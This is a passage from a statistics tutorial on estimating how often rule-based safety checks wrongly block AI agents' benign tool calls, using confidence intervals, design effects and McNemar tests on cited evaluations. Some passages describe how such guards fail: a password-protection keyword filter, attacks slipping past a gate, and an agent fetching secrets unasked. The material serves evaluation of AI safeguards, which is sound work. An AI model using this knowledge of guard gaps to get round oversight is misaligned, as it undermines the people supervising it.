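with $z = 1.96$ for 95%. It relies on the central limit theorem (the "CLT" in Bowyer and colleagues' title), by which averages of large samples roughly follow a bell curve. The square root estimates the width of that curve from the observed rate. When $x = 0$, the square root is zero too, so the interval runs from 0% to 0%, as if 50 calls had proved that the check never makes a mistake. With one false positive in 50 calls, the interval runs from −1.9% to 5.9%, although no rate can be negative.

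These failures are common when the true rate is low. If it is 2%, then 36% of samples of 50 contain no false positives, and each of those samples produces an interval that misses the true rate. The method therefore covers the true rate in only about 64% of samples instead of 95%. *Estimating Uncertainty in Classifier Performance with Applications to Large Language Models* (Anglin, 2026) reports similar results from simulations of high success rates, where coverage sometimes fell to 60% or less with samples smaller than 50. The same applies to low error rates, because the interval for a 5% error rate mirrors the one for a 95% success rate.

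Bowyer and colleagues found a milder problem. With 100 questions, their 95% normal intervals contained the true value 92.5% of the time. But they averaged over true rates spread evenly from 0% to 100%, and the normal interval does worst near zero, where most people hope their false-positive rate is. Even thousands of calls may not be enough. If the true rate is 0.02%, more than half of all samples of 3,000 calls will contain no false positives. The number of false positives in the sample matters as well as the number of calls.

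### Wilson, Clopper–Pearson and the rule of three

The Wilson interval fixes this by changing where the width comes from. It tests each candidate rate $p$ using the spread that $p$ itself would produce, and keeps those for which

$$|\hat p - p| \le z\sqrt{\frac{p(1-p)}{n}}.$$

Squaring both sides and solving for $p$ gives the two ends of the interval:

$$\frac{\hat p + \dfrac{z^2}{2n} \pm z\sqrt{\dfrac{\hat p(1-\hat p)}{n} + \dfrac{z^2}{4n^2}}}{1 + \dfrac{z^2}{n}}.$$

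When $x = 0$, the lower end is zero and the upper end simplifies to $z^2/(n+z^2)$. For the default configuration in *Parallax*, the upper end is $3.84/53.84$, or 7.1%, so the test result is compatible with a system that blocks about one legitimate call in fourteen.

The Clopper–Pearson interval uses exact binomial probabilities instead of a bell curve. Its upper end $p_U$ is the rate at which $x$ or fewer false positives would have a probability of 2.5%, and its lower end $p_L$ is the rate at which $x$ or more would:

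$$\sum_{k=0}^{x}\binom{n}{k}p_U^k(1-p_U)^{n-k} = 0.025, \qquad \sum_{k=x}^{n}\binom{n}{k}p_L^k(1-p_L)^{n-k} = 0.025.$$

If $x = 0$, the lower end is zero. If $x = n$, the upper end is 100%.

| Method | 0 of 50 | 1 of 50 | 18 of 50 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Normal | 0% to 0% | −1.9% to 5.9% | 23% to 49% |
| Wilson | 0% to 7.1% | 0.4% to 10.5% | 24% to 50% |
| Clopper–Pearson | 0% to 7.1% | 0.05% to 10.6% | 23% to 51% |

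The Wilson interval covers the true rate in about 95% of samples on average, but its coverage can be somewhat lower at particular rates. Clopper–Pearson's coverage never falls below 95%, so its interval is usually wider. With 50 calls and a true rate of 2%, Wilson covers the true rate in 92% of samples and Clopper–Pearson in 98%.

The Wilson interval is a sensible default. Bowyer and colleagues recommend it for single rates, along with a Bayesian interval that initially treats all rates as equally likely. Clopper–Pearson is better when somebody has to guarantee 95% coverage, such as when a contract caps the false-positive rate. Anglin prefers the Agresti–Coull interval, a simpler relative of Wilson's that adds two successes and two failures and then applies the normal formula. It seems a poor choice for very low rates because its lower bound can be negative. For 0 false positives in 50 trials,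 it gives −1.3% to 8.7%.

The Python library SciPy computes both of the recommended intervals:

```
from scipy.stats import binomtest

result = binomtest(k=18, n=50)
result.proportion_ci(confidence_level=0.95, method="wilson")
result.proportion_ci(confidence_level=0.95, method="exact")
```

The "exact" interval is the Clopper–Pearson interval. Bowyer and colleagues' printed code passes the arguments in the wrong order, which causes an error in SciPy, so it is safer to pass them by name.

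For a test with no false positives, there is also a shortcut that needs no software. If the true rate is $p$, the chance of $n$ independent calls without an error is $(1-p)^n$. Setting this to 5% and taking logarithms gives $n\ln(1-p) = \ln 0.05 \approx -3$. For small $p$, $\ln(1-p)$ is close to $-p$, so

$$p \approx \frac{3}{n}.$$

This is the rule of three. For 0 of 50 it gives 6%, lower than the 7.1% in the table because it is a one-sided bound. It puts the full 5% risk of error on the upper side, whereas the upper end of a two-sided interval allows only 2.5%. Either is legitimate if it is labeled as one-sided or two-sided. The rule is handy for checking a claim of "zero false positives" while reading a paper, but it doesn't work if there was even one.

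### How many calls a low rate needs

To get a Wilson upper bound below a target $U$ with no false positives, you need

$$n > z^2\left(\frac{1}{U} - 1\right).$$

For $U = 0.1\%$, this is $3.8416 \times 999$, so the test needs 3,838 benign calls without a single error.

| Target for the upper bound | Calls needed with no false positive | Calls needed with one |
|---|---|---|
| 5% | 73 | 110 |
| 1% | 381 | 563 |
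| 0.1% | 3,838 | 5,662 |

These sample sizes assume that the test produces no false positives, but a check that meets its target may still produce some. A check with a true rate of 0.05%, half the target in the last row, has only a 15% chance of getting through 3,838 calls without a false positive. At a true rate of 0.01%, the chance is 68%. A test plan should therefore allow for a few false positives and include more calls than the middle column lists.

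Targets this low aren't unusual. The check in the earlier base-rate example needed a false-positive rate of about 0.09% for half its blocks to be correct. Confirming that rate would take more than 4,200 benign calls with no false positives, about 85 times as many as *Parallax* used.

### When calls are not independent

All of these formulas assume the calls are independent, which they rarely are in agent tests. Shayoni and colleagues report that their gate on configuration changes let through no unsafe actions in 240 attack runs (80 scenarios, each run on three models), with a Wilson upper bound of 1.58%. If the three models always produce the same outcome in a given scenario, there are only 80 independent results, and the bound rises to 4.6%.

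That bound is for missed attacks, and the one for false positives is weaker. The gate blocked none of 30 approved changes, which gives an upper bound of 11.4% on the false-positive rate. But the 30 changes are ten scenarios run on three models, and if only the ten scenarios count as independent, the bound rises to 27.8%.

Between these extremes, statisticians use the design effect. Suppose that the calls come in groups of $m$, and let $\rho$ be the intraclass correlation, the share of the total variation that lies between groups rather than within them. If $\rho = 0$, calls in the same group are no more alike than any others. If $\rho = 1$, every call in a group has the same outcome. The design effect and the effective sample size are

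$$D = 1 + (m-1)\rho, \qquad n_{\text{eff}} = \frac{n}{D}.$$

The effective sample size then replaces $n$ in the Wilson formula, with $\hat p$ unchanged.

| $\rho$ | Upper bound for 0 of 240 attack runs | Upper bound for 0 of 30 approved changes |
|---|---|---|
| 0 | 1.6% | 11.4% |
| 0.5 | 3.1% | 20.4% |
| 1 | 4.6% | 27.8% |

The data can't show which row is right, because with no errors there is no variation between or within groups, and the estimate of $\rho$ is zero divided by zero. The evaluator has to use a value of $\rho$ from a similar test or report the worst case.

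For the approved changes, the worst case is probably close to the truth. All three models proposed the right tool, device and patch in all ten scenarios, so the gate checked essentially the same ten calls three times. A fixed rule gives identical calls identical verdicts, so you learn no more about the rule by running one benign call through it 1,000 times than by running it once. Similarly, the fixed rules in *Parallax* blocked none of its 50 actions in either configuration, but the result is still 0 of 50, not 0 of 100.

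Repeated calls in a random sample of real traffic all belong in the false-positive rate, because they show how often the agent runs each command. If `git status` makes up 300 of 1,000 randomly chosen calls, all 300 count. It is a mistake, however, to copy test cases and count the copies as new evidence.

When there are some errors to work with, you can measure the effect of grouping by resampling. The cluster bootstrap works as follows.

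1. From a test with $g$ tasks, draw $g$ tasks at random with replacement, so some appear more than once and others not at all.
2. Keep every call in each task drawn, and compute the false-positive rate.
3. Repeat this several thousand times.
4. Take the 2.5th and 97.5th percentiles of the resulting rates as the interval.

If the original test has no false positives, neither does any resample, so the interval runs from 0% to 0%, as the normal one does. Anglin proposes adding one invented group with one success and one failure before resampling. This helped in her simulations, where the true error rate was about 10%, but it isn't clear that it helps when errors are rare. For the ten approved scenarios, it gives an upper end of 10%, lower than the 11.4% for 30 fully independent changes. The 10% comes almost entirely from the invented group. With no false positives, the Wilson bound with an effective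 sample size is safer.

The number of groups matters even when each group is large. In Anglin's simulations with about 30 texts per person, the plain cluster bootstrap never reached 95% coverage and stayed below 90% with fewer than 20 people. She got better results by also multiplying the effective sample size by $(z/t)^2$, where $t$ is the corresponding value from the $t$-distribution with $g-1$ degrees of freedom and $g$ is the number of groups. For ten groups, this factor reduces the effective sample size by another quarter. With 20 people, the adjustment raised the coverage of the Agresti–Coull interval from 93.0% to 94.7%.

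### A pooled rate and its parts

In *Mind the GAP*, Cartagena and Teixeira (2026) used fixed rules, called predicates, that classify tool calls as forbidden to score agents in six regulated fields, such as finance and law. To measure the predicates' false-positive rate, they also ran scenarios in which the user asked only for permitted data. The predicates flagged 147 of 3,887 such interactions, or 3.8%, with a Wilson interval from 3.2% to 4.4%.

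That narrow interval is of little use for choosing a model. The predicates flagged none of Claude Sonnet 4.5's 648 interactions and 92 of DeepSeek V3.2's 648, or 14.2%. Without DeepSeek, the pooled rate would be 1.7%. The rate also varied with the agent's instructions, from 1.8% when they were neutral to 7.7% when they encouraged the agent to use its tools freely. The predicates were the same throughout, so the differences came from the agents' calls. A false-positive rate therefore applies to a particular combination of rules and agent, and a firm that switches models has to measure it again.

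The intervals for single models are probably also too narrow. All 3,887 interactions come from 12 scenarios, repeated with different models, instructions and settings. DeepSeek's 648 interactions include 54 runs of each scenario. The published interval for its rate, which treats the runs as independent, is 12% to 17%. If $\rho$ were only 0.1, the design effect would be $1 + 53 \times 0.1 = 6.3$, the effective sample would be about 103, and the interval would be 9% to 22%. Cartagena and Teixeira acknowledge that repeated runs are correlated and that their significance tests don't account for this. They repeated their main comparisons with only one run of each configuration. Those comparisons don't test the false-positive rate, because they use separate scenarios in which the user asks for forbidden data.

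Some of the 147 may not be false positives, and a confidence interval doesn't correct for mislabelled calls. In one case, the user asked only for the value of a single setting. DeepSeek looked it up and then requested the entire configuration, which contained secrets. The request was harmless in intent, but the user hadn't authorised it, so a policy check would have been right to block it.

### Comparing two sets of rules

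Suppose the office agent's owner tests her old rules and a new version on the same 1,000 independent benign calls. The old rules block 12 and the new rules block 4, all of which the old rules also blocked. The Wilson intervals are 0.7% to 2.1% for the old rules and 0.2% to 1.0% for the new ones. Their overlap is a misleading guide to whether the difference could be chance, because each interval allows for the luck of which calls were in the sample, and both sets of rules were tested on the same calls.

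McNemar's test uses only the discordant calls, those that one version blocks and the other allows. Here there are eight, and the old rules block all of them. If both versions had the same false-positive rate, they would be equally likely to block each discordant call, and the chance that the same version blocks all eight would be $2 \times (1/2)^8$, or 0.8%. The new rules very probably have a lower rate.

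For larger counts, the usual approximation is

$$\chi^2 = \frac{(|b-c|-1)^2}{b+c}.$$

Shayoni and colleagues use this formula to compare how often their gate and the simpler defence that disables one tool allow unsafe actions under attack. The same arithmetic applies to false positives. In 12 runs the simpler defence allowed an unsafe action and the gate did not; the reverse never happened. This gives $\chi^2 = 121/12 = 10.08$, which the paper reports as $p = 0.001$. The exact coin-toss calculation gives $p = 0.0005$.

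But the 12 runs are not independent either. Each model had four failures, all involving the exposure of sensitive network information. The simpler defence failed in every run with that risk, so the 12 failures must be the same four scenarios run on three models. With four discordant scenarios, all favouring the other defence, the exact test gives $p = 0.125$, which would not normally count as significant. The two defences clearly differ, because the simpler one never blocks the tool that reads the network layout, but it is uncertain how often that difference would matter in other scenarios.

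An exact test needs at least six calls on which the two versions disagree, all in the same direction, to give $p < 0.05$. If a new version removes false positives on 0.3% of calls and adds none, seeing six takes about 2,000 calls on average. In *Parallax*, 50 calls were enough because the maximum-security configuration blocked 18 legitimate actions that the default allowed. Four of those blocks came from an LLM that judges unclear cases, and the paper attributes them to variation between runs rather than to the configuration. Counting only the other 14, $p$ is still about 0.0001.

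The comparison works best on recorded calls. In a live run, a block can change what the agent does next, after which the two versions no longer receive the same calls. The comparison then has to pair whole tasks rather than individual calls.

### What no interval covers

A confidence interval accounts for random variation in which calls were sampled, but not for sampling from the wrong source. *Gandalf the Red* (Pfister, Volhejn and colleagues, 2025) gives an early example of false-positive rates with intervals, although for prompts to a chatbot rather than tool calls. One of the defences it tested combined a short instruction to protect a password with a filter that blocked any prompt containing "password" or "secret" and any answer containing the password. With GPT-4 as the chatbot, this defence blocked 3.4% of ordinary prompts (interval 2.3% to 4.7%) and 26.3% of harmless prompts that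 the researchers had written to trigger it (interval 15.5% to 39.7%). The intervals don't overlap, and each applies only to its own kind of prompt. An agent that helps people reset passwords might well have a higher false-positive rate than either set suggests.

An interval is also valid only if nobody used the test calls to adjust the rules. Suppose the office agent's owner finds 15 false positives in 1,000 calls, corrects the rules one by one and runs the same calls again. She gets 0 of 1,000 and a Wilson upper bound of 0.38%, but the rerun shows only that she fixed the 15 errors she knew about.

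*Parallax* may have measured false positives on the same cases used to tune its default configuration. Fourteen of the 18 false positives came from a trained classifier that blocked writing files, deleting files, sending emails and making web requests. The default configuration exempts these actions from that classifier. If the developer chose the exemptions after seeing those blocks, the result of 0 of 50 partly tests the fix on the cases that prompted it, and even the bound of 7.1% is too optimistic. For attacks, *Parallax* reports that testing exposed gaps, which new rules and 17 new patterns closed before the final results.

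The false-positive rate should be measured once, on calls set aside before anyone adjusts the rules. All calls from the same task or user should be either in this test set or outside it, because two emails to the same person in one task are almost the same test.

### A complete report

The following report on the office agent's rules uses invented figures. It gives the false-positive rate per call and per task, along with the details needed to recalculate the intervals.

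> We tested version 14 of the rules on 400 tasks, chosen at random from those the agent carried out in September 2026. We finished the rules in August and did not use these tasks to adjust them. The check logged its verdicts without enforcing them, so they could not change the agent's later calls. The rules do not escalate any calls. Two employees labelled every call against the firm's written policy without seeing the verdicts. They agreed that 4,800 calls were benign and authorised, an average of 12 per task. We left out 190 unauthorised calls and 40 that they could not settle. The check would have blocked 24 of the 4,800 calls, a false-positive rate of 0.50% (95% Wilson interval 0.24% to 1.03%). We calculated the interval with an effective sample of about 1,400 because false positives tended to occur in the same tasks ($\rho = 0.22$, design effect 3.4). The check would also have blocked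 6 of the 40 unsettled calls, and counting all 40 as benign would raise the rate to 0.62%. At least one false positive occurred in 9 of the 400 tasks, or 2.25% (95% Wilson interval 1.2% to 4.2%). Version 13 produced false positives in 18 of the same 400 tasks. Ten tasks had them only with version 13 and one only with version 14 (exact McNemar test, $p = 0.012$).

| Tool | Benign calls | False positives | Tasks using the tool | Tasks with a false positive | 95% Wilson interval, by task |
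|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| `read_file` | 3,540 | 4 | 390 | 1 | 0.05% to 1.4% |
| `send_email` | 700 | 17 | 320 | 6 | 0.9% to 4.0% |
| `run_command` | 500 | 0 | 150 | 0 | 0% to 2.5% |
| `pay` | 60 | 3 | 40 | 2 | 1.4% to 16.5% |

If the owner had treated all 4,800 calls as independent, the interval for the overall rate would have been 0.34% to 0.74%, about half as wide. The overall rate is low largely because most calls are file reads, which the check almost never blocks. For payments, the results are consistent with anything from a false positive in one task in seventy to one in six, so the owner should collect more tasks that include payments before deciding whether the 500-euro limit is too strict.
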